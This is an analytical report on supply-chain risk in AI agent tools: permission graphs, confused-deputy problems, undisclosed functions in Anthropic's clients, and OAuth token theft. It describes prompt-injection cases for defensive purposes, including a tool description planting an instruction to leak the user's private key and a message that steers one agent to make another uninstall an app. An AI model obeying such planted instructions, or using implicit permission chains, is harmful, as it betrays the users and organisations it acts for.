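# Supply-chain security of opaque AI agent tools in critical industries

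## What an agent tool is made of and what it can reach

An AI agent tool is a product that lets a large language model, the kind of AI program that produces text, take actions on a person's behalf, such as running commands on a computer, reading mail, changing files or opening a ticket in another company's system. Supply-chain security deals with harm that reaches an organisation through its suppliers, the components inside their products and the updates they send. An organisation that installs an agent tool takes on an unusual supply chain, because the model may come from one company, the connections from several others, and the permissions from whoever set up the accounts years ago.

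Agents increasingly use tools to change things as well as read them. *How are AI agents used?* (Stein, 2026) catalogued 177,436 tools that developers had published for agents between November 2024 and February 2026. Over that period, tools that modify something, such as a file, a bank balance or a web page, rose from 27% to 65% of usage. Stein works at the UK government's AI Security Institute and has no commercial interest in the result. But he estimated usage from downloads, which do not show whether anyone called the tool afterwards, and 90% of the downloads were for software development, so the trend is only weak direct evidence about banks or utilities.

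Critical industries are those whose failure quickly hurts people outside them. US policy has listed 16 such sectors since 2013, among them energy, water, financial services, health care, government services and the defence industrial base, and the EU has a similar list. Security engineers sort the possible harm by what the victim loses: confidentiality, when someone reads what they should not; integrity, when someone alters data or commands; and availability, when a system stops working. The importance of each varies by industry. A bank cannot undo a leak of its customers' accounts, and a false transfer undermines its core service, but an hour without its app is embarrassing and usually survivable. In a waterworks, the pressure readings are hardly secret (plans of the network may be), but a stopped pump, or chlorine dosing that follows a false reading, can affect customers' water within hours.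 A bank can therefore reasonably cut off a suspicious agent at once, while a waterworks first has to know that nothing in operation depends on it.

### From the request to the connected system

At a hypothetical water company, maintenance planners use an agent with four connections: the department's mailbox, the ticket system where staff report faults and order repairs, a read-only store of pump sensor data, and an account on the support portal of the contractor that services the pumps. A planner tells the agent that pump 7 is vibrating and asks it to find out why and schedule a repair.

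Both the request and the authority behind it start with the user. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (Surapani, Kakitapelli et al., 2026) describes five layers of authority: the person, the organisation that deploys the agent, the main agent, any sub-agents it starts, and the tools. Every action further down should trace back to something the person delegated, stay within it, and remain open to challenge afterwards. The paper's review of 89 sources found few documented deployments that do all of this reliably. The user is easier to inspect than the other layers, because the company employs her and can log everything she types.

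Her sentence goes to the client, the part of the tool that runs on her own computer. The client assembles what the model will see, sends it to the vendor and carries out the actions that come back. The vendor supplies the client and usually updates it. According to Anthropic's setup guide, a standard installation of Claude Code, an agent tool for programmers, checks for new versions at startup and while running, installs them in the background and switches to them at the next start. A company can instead follow a "stable" channel about a week behind, fix a permitted range of versions for all its machines, or block updates altogether. It can also compare the program's checksum, a short fingerprint of the file, with a list that Anthropic signs. A match shows that the file is the one Anthropic released, but not what the program does. Most vendors keep their source code private. *The 2025 AI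 Agent Index* (Staufer, Feng and colleagues, 2026) found that 23 of 30 prominent agent products were fully closed, while the other seven published the framework around the model.

The model receives the planner's sentence along with the system prompt, which contains standing instructions on what the product is for, which tools the model may call and how it should respond. The vendor writes most of the system prompt, and the water company can usually add some lines of its own. Text stored in the client changes when the client updates, but the vendor can change the text it adds on its own servers at any time, without changing anything on the customer's machines. A determined customer can capture what the client sends, but nobody outside the vendor sees what the vendor adds afterwards.

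The model runs on the vendor's servers or another company's. It takes in all this text and generates more, either an answer or a structured request, here something like "fetch the vibration readings for pump 7, past 30 days". The client carries out the request and sends the result back as further text, and the loop repeats until the repair is on the calendar. Nearly all the products in the Index ran on OpenAI's GPT, Anthropic's Claude or Google's Gemini, so a waterworks and its bank may well depend on the same model without knowing it. The developer trains and replaces the model. Customers can often choose a named version for as long as the developer keeps serving it, and they can test how it responds, but they cannot look inside it. Staufer and colleagues note that with HubSpot's agent builder, too, the business that deploys an agent cannot inspect the model's behaviour, and the platform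 cannot foresee every use.

The client needs an add-on to reach the sensor store. Some add-ons are skills, which are packages of written instructions that often include scripts. Others are MCP servers, programs that offer agents data or actions through the Model Context Protocol. This protocol is a common connection standard, and 20 of the Index's 30 products supported it. Anyone can publish either kind of add-on, and attackers have published malicious skills. Stein found that by February 2026, AI coding tools were helping write 62% of new MCP servers, up from 6% thirteen months earlier.

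A skill sits on the customer's disk, where staff can read every line, and it changes only when someone replaces it. An MCP server may run on someone else's computer, where its operator can change it after the water company has checked it, and the agent will then use the changed version. CrowdStrike's *How Agentic Tool Chain Attacks Threaten AI Agent Security* (2026) describes this case and another in which a tool adds two numbers, but the description that the model reads contains an instruction to first open the user's private login key and pass its contents along as a side note. The code adds correctly, so a scan of it finds nothing wrong. CrowdStrike sells protection against such attacks, and its cases are illustrations rather than real incidents, but the mechanism follows from the fact that a model receives its tools as text.

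The MCP server opens the sensor store with an access token, a stored credential that lets the program connect without logging in again. The system being accessed issues the token, typically after an employee has clicked through a consent page, and the token works until it expires or someone revokes it. The water company can list the tokens its own systems have issued, but it cannot see how well an add-on's maker protects its copy. Anyone who steals a token gets the agent's access. Surapani and colleagues distinguish authentication, which establishes who is calling, from authorization, which establishes whether this caller may do this particular thing for this particular person. A valid token is good evidence of the caller's identity but hardly shows whether the request is authorized.

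The connected systems are the last part. The water company runs or rents its mailbox, ticket system and sensor store, schedules their updates, keeps their logs and decides who has which rights. The contractor owns the support portal, decides when to update it and shows the customer little beyond the login page and the open requests.

### Parts that arrive while the tool runs

*Agentic AI as a Cybersecurity Attack Surface* (Jiang, Yang and colleagues, 2026) distinguishes the static supply chain of an ordinary program from the dynamic supply chain of an agent. Developers of an ordinary program declare the code libraries they need, and the build process fetches them. Each name maps to one particular file that anyone can check before the program reaches a customer. The documents an agent reads and the tools it calls depend instead on the task and on what it found in earlier steps. In the paper's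 example, an agent that books corporate travel searches the web for hotels near a conference in Berlin and reads a blog post that promises a corporate discount through a booking interface. It then downloads and runs the code library that the post recommends, although nobody at the company had vetted the post or the library when the agent went into service.

Jiang and colleagues divide tool use into three steps, each with its own risks. Discovery turns an intention into the name of a tool. Models sometimes invent package names, and if an attacker has already registered one of them, the agent downloads the attacker's package. Implementation loads the code behind the name, and installation may run other packages' code before the tool starts. Invocation runs the tool with particular inputs and credentials, and even the right tool with genuine code can do something the user never asked for. Ordinary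 components flow from maker to user, but an agent's output, such as a ticket or a company wiki page, can later become input to the same agent or another one, so a customer can also be its own supplier.

The contrast with ordinary software is not absolute. Such software also fetches things after its release, as every web browser does, and an operator can make an agent more static by permitting only a short, fixed list of tools. A bill of materials, a machine-readable list of a product's components, versions and suppliers, could then cover the tools fairly well. It could not cover the text the agent reads, because a maintenance agent must read new mail or tickets to be useful.

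### Opaque logic and implicit permission links

Tools built this way raise two problems that call for different checks. The first is opaque logic, which is behaviour that the customer cannot inspect, reproduce or predict from what the vendor discloses. It sits in the closed client, the part of the system prompt that the vendor adds, the model and any add-on that runs elsewhere. A customer who suspects something has little to check the suspicion against, although opacity is not a sign of malice. Of the 30 products in the Index, 25 disclosed no results of internal safety tests. Staufer and colleagues worked only from public information and developers' replies, and only four developers sent substantive comments, so a large bank with a good contract may know more than the Index reports.

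An implicit permission link is access that an agent has through a default, a shared account or a connected tool, although nobody approved that particular use. In *Agent Approval Laundering*, Zhang, Xia and colleagues (2026) measured a small, well-defined version of it, in which a person approves one command from a coding agent and that command sets off others. In one run, Claude Code asked to install the packages for Vite, a web-development project, and the approval named the exact install command. The installer then started a follow-up script and wrote to the project's folder. The approval record, as the researchers encoded it, covered running a program but not changing any files.

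The researchers compared 111 such records with what then happened on the machine, sorting the effects into six broad classes, such as file changes and network connections. Counting only what was stated outright, 40 of the records left out at least one class of effect that occurred. Adding general knowledge of what such commands do reduced that number to 17, and adding the project's own configuration files, which anyone could have read before approving, reduced it to 13. Much of the missing information was therefore available when the person decided whether to approve, but the record did not show it.

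Zhang and colleagues also prove a limit on any rule that decides from the approval record alone. If two runs look identical in the record, but a policy must allow one (it only runs a local script) and refuse the other (the script also fetches something from the internet), the rule must treat both alike, so it gets at least one of them wrong some of the time. Adding information to the record can help. When the researchers added predicted effects, the number of effects missing from the records of 17 test workflows fell from 10 to 3. However, 17 of 18 cases then required a second approval, and people who are asked that often may stop reading the requests. The paper acknowledges that the problem is not specific to AI, since the same chain unfolds when a person types the command. An agent adds a formal approval that looks as if it covers the whole chain.

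### The confused deputy

An implicit permission link becomes dangerous when an outsider can steer the program that holds it. Security engineers call such a program a confused deputy because someone tricks it into using its own authority on their behalf. The term comes from Hardy's 1988 paper *The Confused Deputy*, which tells a "nearly true" story about Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. Customers who used its compiler, a program that translates source code, could name a file to receive debugging output. The compiler also had permission to write in its own directory because it kept usage statistics there, and the same directory held the billing records. One user named the billing file as the destination for his debugging output. The operating system allowed the write because the compiler had permission, and the compiler overwrote the billing records.

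Hardy argued that the compiler held authority from two sources and had no way to specify which one to use for a given file. Checking for forbidden file names would not have helped for long, because the number of sensitive files keeps growing. His remedy was the capability, a reference that identifies a particular file and carries the right to use it. To make the compiler use the billing file, the user would then have had to supply a capability for that file, which he did not have.

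This fault is harder to fix in agents. A programmer could tell apart the purposes for which Hardy's compiler produced its statistics and its debugging output, but a model receives the planner's request, the system prompt and the body of a stranger's email as one run of text. In prompt injection, an attacker exploits this by planting instructions in material that the agent will read, and the model follows them as if the user had given them. *Taming Various Privilege Escalation in LLM-Based Agent Systems* (2026) gives an example with two agents. A user asks the agent that handles text messages to read out a new one. The message contains an instruction to have the settings agent uninstall Slack, a workplace chat program. The message agent forwards the request to the settings agent, which manages the system's configuration.

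Surapani and colleagues therefore classify prompt injection as a way to bypass authorization, because the agent acts on content from the outermost layer with the authority of the person at the top. If they are right, training models to ignore planted instructions helps but is not enough, and something outside the model has to check each action as it happens. They also list the lack of such checks among the field's main gaps.

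### The water company's permissions as a graph

*A Framework for Formalizing LLM Agent Security* (2026) defines a permission graph G = (S, R), where S is a set of sources, such as users, calendars and the agent itself, and R is a set of ordered pairs of those sources. The pair (s₁, s₂) belongs to R when s₁ has permission to access or influence s₂. Each pair is an edge, drawn as an arrow from s₁ to s₂. In the water company's case, the systems that somebody approved for the agent are one edge away from it, but the agent may be able to affect any system it can reach by following a chain of arrows.

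One edge leads from the maintenance agent to each of its four connections, and the manager who signed the request form saw four lines. Further edges start from there:

- The company's purchasing portal sends its password-reset links to the mailbox.
- An urgent entry in the ticket system automatically books a crew in the scheduling system, and attachments go to a shared document store that also holds drawings of the pipe network.
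- From the sensor store, which the agent can only read, no edge leads on.
- A request on the contractor's portal can open a session on the contractor's remote-maintenance server, and that server can change settings on the pump controllers.

The company approved four systems directly, and the tool could reach five more through further links: the purchasing portal, the scheduling system, the document store, the maintenance server and the pump controllers. Nine is an upper bound, because a link may carry too little influence to pass anything on. For example, the contractor may have an engineer read every request before a session opens. If the company keeps its control network separate from such outside connections, the last link does not exist. The four-line form does not show whether either safeguard is in place.

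Some edges also point towards the agent. For this reason, Surapani and colleagues keep two separate graphs, one for delegation (who passed authority to whom) and one for information (where content comes from and where it can flow). The mailbox belongs in both, because the agent has permission to read it and anyone can write to it. A stranger's email can travel from the mailbox to the agent, then to the contractor's portal, the maintenance server and the pumps. Someone had a reason to allow each of those four edges. The information graph also has a path out of the sensor store, since the agent can email whatever it reads there. A waterworks will worry more about the path to the pumps, but a bank with the same layout, and customer accounts in place of vibration readings, has at least as much to fear from the outgoing mail.

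Closing the contractor's account would cut the number of systems the tool can reach from nine to six. The company did make the sensor store read-only, which protects the readings from alteration but leaves all nine systems within reach.

### How many agents act without sign-off

Figures on how common such arrangements are come mostly from companies that sell a remedy. UpGuard, whose software looks for misconfigurations and overly broad permissions, examined more than 18,000 agent configuration files in public repositories on GitHub, the code-sharing site. *Developers' AI agents pose rising software supply risks* (Salmon, 2026) reports that about one in five developers had enabled high-risk actions without human oversight. Nearly 20% of the files let an agent save changes to the main code repository without review, and 14.5% let it run any Python code. These settings are better evidence than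 opinions, but they belong to programmers who publish their work, and a utility's internal settings could be stricter or laxer.

Enterprise Management Associates surveyed 202 IT and security leaders for Cequence, which sells protection for AI agents. According to Cequence, 94% were confident that their agents had no more access than they needed, while 33% gave agents the least access that would do the job. SecureWorld's *Enterprises Say Their AI Agents Are Secure; the Data Say Otherwise* (2026) presents this as a gap between what organisations believe and what they have verified, which seems right. The survey does not show that the remaining agents have too much access, because an agent with broad standing permissions may need them all, though its owner cannot know that without checking.

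Zorz (2026), in *AI agent permissions are outrunning security*, reports on a survey of 1,100 IT and security decision-makers, 70% of whom let AI take decisions and actions that would have required a person's approval a year earlier. Some 84% claimed to have visibility into how AI systems access their data and systems, but only 49% could see and audit every action an agent takes. Zorz's explanation for the lax permissions comes from a vice-president at Illumio, which has a commercial interest in the issue because it sells software for restricting connections inside a network. The AI Agent Index, compiled mainly by university researchers, also provides evidence of poor logging, though not of lax permissions. According to public documentation at the end of 2025, 12 of its 30 products offered no usage monitoring or only notified users when they reached the rate limit. Some companies may be unable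 to audit their agents because the products they bought do not provide the means to do so.

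## Undisclosed functions in a vendor's client: Claude Code and Claude Desktop

Even when a vendor keeps its client's source code private, the program itself is on the customer's disk, where a patient programmer can take it apart. In 2026 outsiders examined two Anthropic products this way and found a function in each that the company had not disclosed to users. One function marked certain requests from Claude Code, and the other prepared a connection between users' web browsers and Claude Desktop, Anthropic's chat application for personal computers.

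The Claude Code function became public on 30 June. *Hidden code in Claude Code secretly flagged Chinese users* (The Decoder, 2026) credits the discovery to LegitMichel777, a Reddit user. The same day, a developer writing as Thereallo, who had been checking version 2.1.196 for privacy problems, published the relevant code in *Claude Code Is Steganographically Marking Requests* (2026) and noted that Anthropic had signed the file. Schmalbach (2026), in *Claude Code Is Quietly Fingerprinting China-Linked API Routers*, examined older releases and found that version 2.1.90 simply gave the model the date, while 2.1.91, released on 2 April, was the first to pass the date through a new function. According to LegitMichel777, the release notes did not mention it. *Did Anthropic secretly monitor Chinese Claude Code users?* (2026) describes another report, on GitHub, that found the mechanism in versions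 2.1.193, 2.1.195 and 2.1.196. All of these investigations used files that anyone could download, so others could repeat them.

### How the marker worked

Claude Code normally sends its requests to api.anthropic.com, but the setting ANTHROPIC_BASE_URL can redirect them to another server. Some companies use it to route requests through an internal gateway, researchers use it for experiments, and resellers of unofficial access to Claude depend on it. If the setting was unchanged or pointed to Anthropic's own address, the function returned the ordinary line "Today's date is 2026-06-30." and did nothing else. Headlines about "Chinese users" were therefore too broad. Schmalbach points out that someone who used the official address through a VPN, which disguises a user's location, would have sent an unmarked line.

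With any other address, the client ran three tests. It first compared the server's name with a list of 147 domains, which included Chinese companies such as Baidu and Alibaba and apparent resellers such as claude-opus.top. A name matched if it was the same as an entry or a subdomain of one. The first entry was just "cn", so every address under China's national domain matched. The client then searched the name for 11 keywords, including "deepseek", "moonshot" and "zhipu", which are Chinese AI developers. Another keyword, "minimax", is both a Chinese AI developer and a standard term in game theory, so a university server named after the minimax theorem would also have matched. Finally, the client checked whether the computer's time zone was Asia/Shanghai or Asia/Urumqi.

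Neither list appeared in the program as readable text, so a search for "baidu" would have found nothing. Anthropic had disguised each character using XOR with the key 91, then encoded the result in base64, a common way to represent data as letters and digits. XOR flips selected bits, and repeating it with the same key restores them. For example, "cn" becomes "85" before the base64 step, because XOR with 91 changes the character codes 99 and 110 to 56 and 53. The key was in the same program, so the disguise could only stop a casual search.

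The client reported the results through punctuation, a form of steganography (hiding a message in something that looks ordinary). If the time zone was Chinese, the client wrote the date with slashes instead of hyphens. It chose the apostrophe in "Today's" from four nearly identical characters, based on the results of the two address tests. Four apostrophes and two date formats make eight possible lines, so each line carries three bits, one per test. The table lists the bits in the order domain, keyword, time zone, with 1 for a match.

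| Server address | Apostrophe | Bytes sent (UTF-8) | Date with hyphens | Date with slashes |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| No match | U+0027 (the ordinary one) | 27 | 000 | 001 |
| On the domain list only | U+2019 | E2 80 99 | 100 | 101 |
| Contains a keyword only | U+02BC | CA BC | 010 | 011 |
| Both | U+02B9 | CA B9 | 110 | 111 |

Schmalbach reproduced the function on his own machine and published several lines it generates. One reads "Todayʹs date is 2026/06/30." The slashes mean the computer runs on Chinese time. The apostrophe is U+02B9, which means the server's name is on the domain list and contains a keyword. The line therefore decodes to 111, which matches the actual settings, the address deepseek.cn and the time zone Asia/Shanghai. The line does not reveal the address itself, since moonshot.ai would have produced the same apostrophe. State 000 produces the same line as an unchanged server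 address, so only the other seven states are identifiable.

A bank that routed its staff's requests through its own gateway would have unknowingly switched on these tests. Staff in its London office would have sent an ordinary line, but a colleague visiting from Shanghai with a laptop still set to Shanghai time would have sent one with slashes. Thereallo argues that the function mostly caught developers like these, with unusual but legitimate set-ups, because a serious adversary could change the server's name or the time zone, or alter the program.

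The marked line went first to the custom server, whose operator could read it. It reached Anthropic only if that server forwarded the full prompt. Schmalbach recorded no live traffic and does not claim that every server forwarded it. The Decoder's statement that Anthropic could read the marker "instantly" goes beyond what he or Thereallo tested, though the marker would be pointless unless Anthropic expected to receive it at least sometimes.

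### Anthropic's explanation and the Chinese response

Thariq Shihipar, an engineer on the Claude Code team, confirmed the function on X. The Decoder quotes him as calling it "an experiment we launched in March" to prevent account abuse by unauthorised resellers and protect against distillation, in which someone trains a model on another model's outputs to copy its abilities. He said the team had since introduced stronger protections, had been meaning to remove the code for a while, and would do so fully in the next day's release. In Schmalbach's comparison, the code first appears publicly in April. The experiment may have started inside the company in March, or Shihipar may have been slightly wrong about the date.

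The motive is believable. Belanger (2026), in *Secret Claude tracker shocks users after Anthropic’s anti-surveillance stance*, cites a Washington Post finding that $100-a-month subscriptions were on sale for as little as $12. According to Quartz, Anthropic had also accused entities affiliated with Alibaba, the Chinese technology company, of using about 25,000 fraudulent accounts for nearly 28.8 million exchanges with its models in roughly six weeks. Alibaba had not publicly responded to the accusation. The list also names resellers and AI developers, as one would expect if it served the purpose Shihipar gave.

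His explanation does not account for the secrecy. 屠 (2026), in *偷藏3个月，Anthropic删除识别“中国AI”的隐藏代码，官方回应*, an article for the Chinese developer site CSDN, notes that Anthropic neither denied the technical findings nor said why it had not disclosed the mechanism. Anthropic could have announced that it classified custom server addresses without publishing the list, as Schmalbach suggests. Secrecy makes the test harder for resellers to evade, but anyone willing to take the program apart could evade it anyway.

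Alibaba responded before the Chinese government did. On 3 July the South China Morning Post reported a staff memo that, in the translation Belanger quotes, described Claude Code as "recently discovered to carry back-door risks" and put it on a list of high-risk software. Alibaba's ban on the tool took effect on 10 July. Security Magazine's *China Claims “Backdoor” Security Risk in Claude Code, Anthropic Responds* (2026) reports that employees had to switch to Qoder, Alibaba's own AI assistant. An anonymous source told Reuters that Alibaba also imposed the ban because it could face legal and compliance trouble if Anthropic caught it breaking the terms of use. The ban is weak evidence about the software because Alibaba had several reasons to impose it, including its competing product and Anthropic's recent accusation that it had copied Anthropic's models.

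On 8 July China's National Vulnerability Database, a government platform, warned that Claude Code versions 2.1.91 to 2.1.196 contained "security backdoor vulnerabilities". These versions were released from 2 April to 29 June, and the first is the same version as in Schmalbach's finding. The database alleged that the tool could send information about users' location and identity to remote servers without their consent. It advised people to uninstall the affected versions or update to the newest one, and told organisations to review how their development tools connect to outside networks. Quartz reports that Anthropic had removed the code from the newest version. Anthropic replied that the mechanism had been an experimental measure against abuse, and that the company does not allow the use of Claude in China.

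### Testing the words "backdoor" and "spyware"

A backdoor is a hidden function that gives someone access to a system or changes its behaviour under conditions the user does not know. Nobody has shown that the marker gave anyone access. eWeek's *China’s Claude Code Backdoor Warning Deepens Enterprise AI Security Divide* (2026) reports that no public independent audit had found remote control, arbitrary code execution or source code theft. The functions that Thereallo printed read two settings and write one line of text. The second part of the definition fits better, because the client did change its output under conditions users could not see, although it changed at most three characters (one apostrophe and two date separators). The term would apply in a more serious sense if Anthropic's servers gave marked users different answers, but the client does not show whether they did.

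Spyware gathers information about people and passes it on without their knowledge. Taken literally, that definition covers the marker, but most people associate the word with stolen passwords, messages or files, and the marker consisted of three yes-or-no answers. The allegation about location and identity is also only partly right. The time zone gives some indication of location, though people can set it to anything, and the marker by itself identifies nobody. But in the code that Thereallo printed, the same block of context also includes the user's email address in plain text if the client has it. Anyone who received both could link the marker to a person. Schmalbach, who rejects the label "proven spyware", calls the function "covert route fingerprinting", which describes what the code does and leaves open what happened afterwards.

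The most systematic attempt to sort the claims comes from Antiy, a Chinese security company. Antiy's *From Paper "Preannouncement" to Crossing the Line* (2026) contains an evidence matrix that grades each claim by the strength of its support:

- **In the client:** Antiy rates the evidence that the program contained the tests and hid their results in the prompt as moderate to high. It stops short of "strong" because the reproduction covers specific versions. Since several people found the same code and an Anthropic engineer confirmed the experiment, this seems cautious.
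- **On the servers:** Antiy calls it a reasonable inference that Anthropic used the markers to block users, give them a weaker service or send their requests to a different model, but says that it cannot verify this.
- **Spyware or code theft:** Antiy finds insufficient evidence, because nobody has shown the theft of any information beyond the marker.

Antiy also finds strong evidence of a problem with transparency and trust. This finding is partly a value judgement, but its factual basis is solid because the client hid the results where ordinary users would not see them.

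Elsewhere in the report, Antiy is less careful about the servers and says one can infer that Anthropic used these methods to strengthen its blocking. The main support for this inference is timing. 虎嗅网's *Claude Code 被曝用隐写术标记中国用户 引发隐私信任危机* (2026), a commentary by a Chinese blogger who had just lost one of his two paid accounts, reports that Anthropic was closing almost all accounts in China at the time. But Anthropic could have found those accounts in other ways. The commentary also alleges that the company put address tracking in the emails it sent to people it had banned, and Shihipar said the team had stronger protections by then. Only Anthropic's internal records could show whether a marker ever led to a ban.

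Antiy says it writes "from the perspective of China's national security interests". It spends much of the report arguing that Anthropic's regional restrictions are unjust, and it wants China to develop independent AI systems for key sectors. Its rejection of the spyware charge is more credible because the charge would have suited its case. Its preferred term, "backdoor risk", deserves more suspicion. The term matches Alibaba's wording, and Antiy notes that its view agrees with that of the national authorities, but the evidence concerns a marker, and a backdoor is only a possibility. Antiy also compares the marker with experiments on conditional behaviour trained into models, though it concedes that these do not show such behaviour in Claude.

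The dates in the English version, which is a machine translation, are unreliable. It places both the Reddit post and the controversy in March 2026, although its reference list links to a news report from 1 July. The error probably comes from confusion with the month the experiment began. Tom's Hardware's *China alleges that Claude Code contains backdoors, calls mechanism 'a serious threat'* (2026) makes the opposite mistake and says the experiment began in June.

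### The browser link in Claude Desktop

Two months earlier, the privacy consultant Alexander Hanff was checking which outside programs his Brave browser could start when he found an entry from Anthropic. He had installed Claude Desktop on his Mac but none of Anthropic's browser extensions. His account, That Privacy Guy's *Anthropic silently installed a spyware bridge on my machine*, appeared in April 2026.

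The entry belonged to native messaging, a standard feature of Chromium, the software on which Chrome, Edge, Brave and several other browsers are built. Browsers run web pages and extensions in a sandbox, which separates them from the rest of the computer. Native messaging lets an extension communicate with a program outside the sandbox. The program's maker places a small text file, called a manifest, in a folder that the browser reads. The manifest lists the program's name, its location on the disk and the extensions that may call it. When an extension requests the program, the browser looks up the manifest, checks the extension's identification code, starts the program and passes messages between the two. The program runs with the rights of the logged-in user.

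Hanff then audited a second machine and found that Claude Desktop had written identical manifests into the folders of seven browsers: Chrome, Edge, Brave, Arc, Vivaldi, Opera and Chromium. Each manifest pointed to a helper program inside Claude Desktop and authorised three extensions to start it. Only Chrome and Brave were installed. (Hanff counts four missing browsers, but his own listing shows five.) If the owner later installed one of the others, its manifest would already be in place. According to Anthropic's documentation, a similar feature of Claude Code worked with Chrome and Edge but did not yet support Brave or Arc.

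The evidence that Claude Desktop wrote these files is strong. Its log recorded 31 completed installations, and macOS had attached the same mark of origin to the log and to the two manifests Hanff checked. The oldest manifest dated from 20 December 2025 and the other six from 19 January 2026, and the application had rewritten all seven on 16 April. Hanff concludes that it rewrites them at every launch, so a deleted file comes back. Antiy's *Risk Analysis of Unauthorized Pre-Configuration of High-Privilege Browser Communication Channels* (2026) also describes files returning after a restart. Anthropic had done much less to conceal this function than the marker in Claude Code. The manifests were readable text containing the company's name, but the application had not asked for permission or told the user where to find them.

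Hanff calls the connection a backdoor and "spyware capability", but he also writes that it does nothing until it is used. The helper starts only when one of the three extensions calls it, and he had none of them installed. With an extension in place, Anthropic's documentation describes an agent that shares the browser's login state, reads pages, fills in forms and records sessions. If an employee were logged in to a bank's administration console, the agent would have the same access. The manifest therefore permits the connection in advance, and someone who later agrees to install the extension will never have agreed to the helper. Separate browser profiles for work and private use would not help, since Hanff says that a manifest applies to the whole browser.

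Hanff lists several ways an attacker could exploit the connection and labels them as scenarios. In one, an attacker who compromises an authorised extension can immediately start a program outside the sandbox. He says the attacker would otherwise have to write the manifest first, which would trigger a prompt or require higher privileges. Claude Desktop wrote seven manifests without a prompt, so this obstacle may be small for an attacker who already runs programs on the machine. It is larger for one who controls only an extension, because the extension is still inside the sandbox.

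Another scenario involves prompt injection. In Anthropic's own tests of its Chrome extension, such attacks succeeded 23.6% of the time without safeguards and 11.2% with them. Hanff summarises this as roughly one in four, but users had the version with safeguards, where the rate was about one in nine. Both figures are success rates for deliberate attacks in a test, so they do not measure how often customers will be attacked.

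Nobody has shown that data was stolen, and Hanff's audit was unlikely to reveal theft. He examined files, logs and signatures on machines that had no extension to call the helper, and he did not record any data leaving. Malwarebytes' *Researcher claims Claude Desktop installs “spyware” on macOS* (2026) concludes that the spyware label is unfair, but that the application enlarged the attack surface (the number of places an attacker can try) without asking for consent. Malwarebytes sells security software, including a browser extension, though its verdict is milder than the claim it was assessing. In its evidence matrix, Antiy rates the silent writing of the files as strongly supported, but it says in an appendix to the same report that nobody has proved malicious data theft.

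Anthropic's response is less clear. Malwarebytes had found no rebuttal by 22 April and was waiting for a reply to its own enquiry. Hanff then formally demanded, in That Privacy Guy's *Media coverage since the initial post*, that Anthropic remove the manifests within 72 hours. In his legal opinion, the installation broke Article 5(3) of the EU's ePrivacy Directive, which requires consent for storing information on a user's device unless this is strictly necessary for a service the user has requested. Antiy reports that Anthropic later added an authorisation switch, which Antiy elsewhere calls a pop-up, but left the underlying permissions largely unchanged. Antiy gives no version number or date for the change, so a customer should install the current version on a test machine and check the folders before relying on it.

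### Which checks could have found the two functions

Checking the vendor's signature would not have revealed either function, because Anthropic had signed both the Claude Code program and the helper in Claude Desktop, and it intended to release the functions as part of them. Attestation, which proves which software a computer is running, would have confirmed that the computer was running those genuine files.

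Comparing releases could have exposed the marker in April, when version 2.1.91 replaced a plain line of text in 2.1.90 with a call to a function that read the server address and the time zone. But a reviewer would have needed a copy of the old version, which automatic updates replace in the background. Comparison is also laborious because Anthropic ships the code in compressed form, with short, meaningless function names that change from build to build. In version 2.1.196, the function had one name in the Linux package that Schmalbach opened and another in Thereallo's copy. A search for suspicious company names would have failed because they were disguised, but the names of the two time zones are readable in the code that Thereallo printed. It makes more sense to look for what a program reads, such as location settings and server addresses, than for suspicious words. Even then, a reviewer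 learns only what the program can do, and would still have to find out whether the conditions apply on the company's own machines.

Inspecting outgoing requests shows only what a program sends under the conditions of the test. Someone in Berlin who used Anthropic's official address could have examined every byte and found nothing. Pointing ANTHROPIC_BASE_URL at a recording program to capture the traffic would have activated the client's checks, but the line would still have looked normal if the computer ran on Berlin time and the recorder's name matched neither list. A tester has to repeat the same request, changing one setting at a time. Changing the time zone to Shanghai would have turned the hyphens into slashes, which are easy to see. The apostrophes would have been harder to find, because the tester would also have had to guess a server name that matched one of the lists.

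The comparison has to use raw bytes because, as Antiy warns, many logging systems convert similar characters to a single form, which would have erased the difference between 27 and CA B9. Antiy advises companies that connect through a gateway to keep complete request logs and snapshots of the system prompt. With those records, a company could have determined in July which of its requests since April carried a marker. The logs need strong protection because they contain everything employees sent to the model.

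Watching file changes would have found the browser link on the first day. An administrator who lists the files on a clean machine before and after installing Claude Desktop will see new manifests in the browser folders, and can then delete them and restart the application to check whether they return. This takes no reverse engineering, and a company could repeat it for every update. Comparing files would have missed the Claude Code marker, because that function only changed text in a request. It also does not show what the helper does once an extension calls it. Malwarebytes noted that Anthropic had published no detailed account of what data flows between browser and application, and that most of the testing was done on Macs, so the behaviour on Windows and Linux was still unclear. To answer these questions, a tester would have to install an authorised extension and record the messages.

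None of these checks reaches the vendor's servers. A customer who has decoded a marker still does not know whether Anthropic stored it, for how long, or whether it influenced the answers. A vendor can also impose undisclosed restrictions entirely on its own servers, without involving the client. *Anthropic walks back covert capability limits on Claude Fable 5* (Goldman, 2026) reported in June that the company had reversed hidden limits on one of its models after AI researchers and developers accused it of "secret sabotage". A customer could look for server-side limits only in the answers, by giving the model the same tasks from differently configured accounts over a long period, and even a consistent difference would not show what had caused it.

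## Components that hold other systems' keys: Salesloft Drift and LiteLLM

Two suppliers lost control of secrets that customers had entrusted to their AI tools, whereas no one has shown that the hidden functions in Claude Code and Claude Desktop led to any loss of customer data. In August 2025, attackers used access tokens from Drift, a chat agent for sales teams, to copy records from other companies' systems. In March 2026, attackers published malicious versions of LiteLLM, a gateway that passes requests to many model providers and stores the keys to them. Another attack on LiteLLM in October combined the two methods.

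### How Drift got its tokens

Drift is a chatbot that talks to visitors on a company's website and refers promising ones to the sales staff. Its owner, Salesloft, offered connections to other software, especially Salesforce, where many companies keep customer records and support tickets. To connect the two, an administrator typically clicks a button in Drift and logs in on Salesforce's own page with her password and a second factor, such as a code from her phone. Salesforce then shows her the permissions Drift requests. If she agrees, Salesforce issues tokens to Drift under OAuth, the usual standard for delegating access, and Drift never receives her password.

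OAuth commonly involves two tokens. Drift sends the access token with each request, and this token often expires within hours. The refresh token, which Drift uses to get new access tokens, lasts much longer, in many systems until someone revokes it. The administrator needs her password and second factor only when she gives consent, because the chat agent also has to work when nobody is there to type a code. A thief who copies a token can therefore use the connection without logging in.

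The permissions she agreed to are the token's scope. A scope can be as narrow as reading contacts, but many systems also offer one that covers everything the approving account is allowed to do. If an administrator approves that scope, the token gets broad access.

### Ten days of copying

According to Salesloft's preliminary findings, summarised in The Record's *Salesloft*, an intruder had access to the company's GitHub account from March to June 2025, downloaded material from several repositories and explored the systems behind both Salesloft and Drift. The intruder then entered Drift's environment at Amazon Web Services (AWS), a cloud provider, and took the tokens for customers' connections. CyberScoop noted at the time that Salesloft had not explained how the intruder got into the GitHub account.

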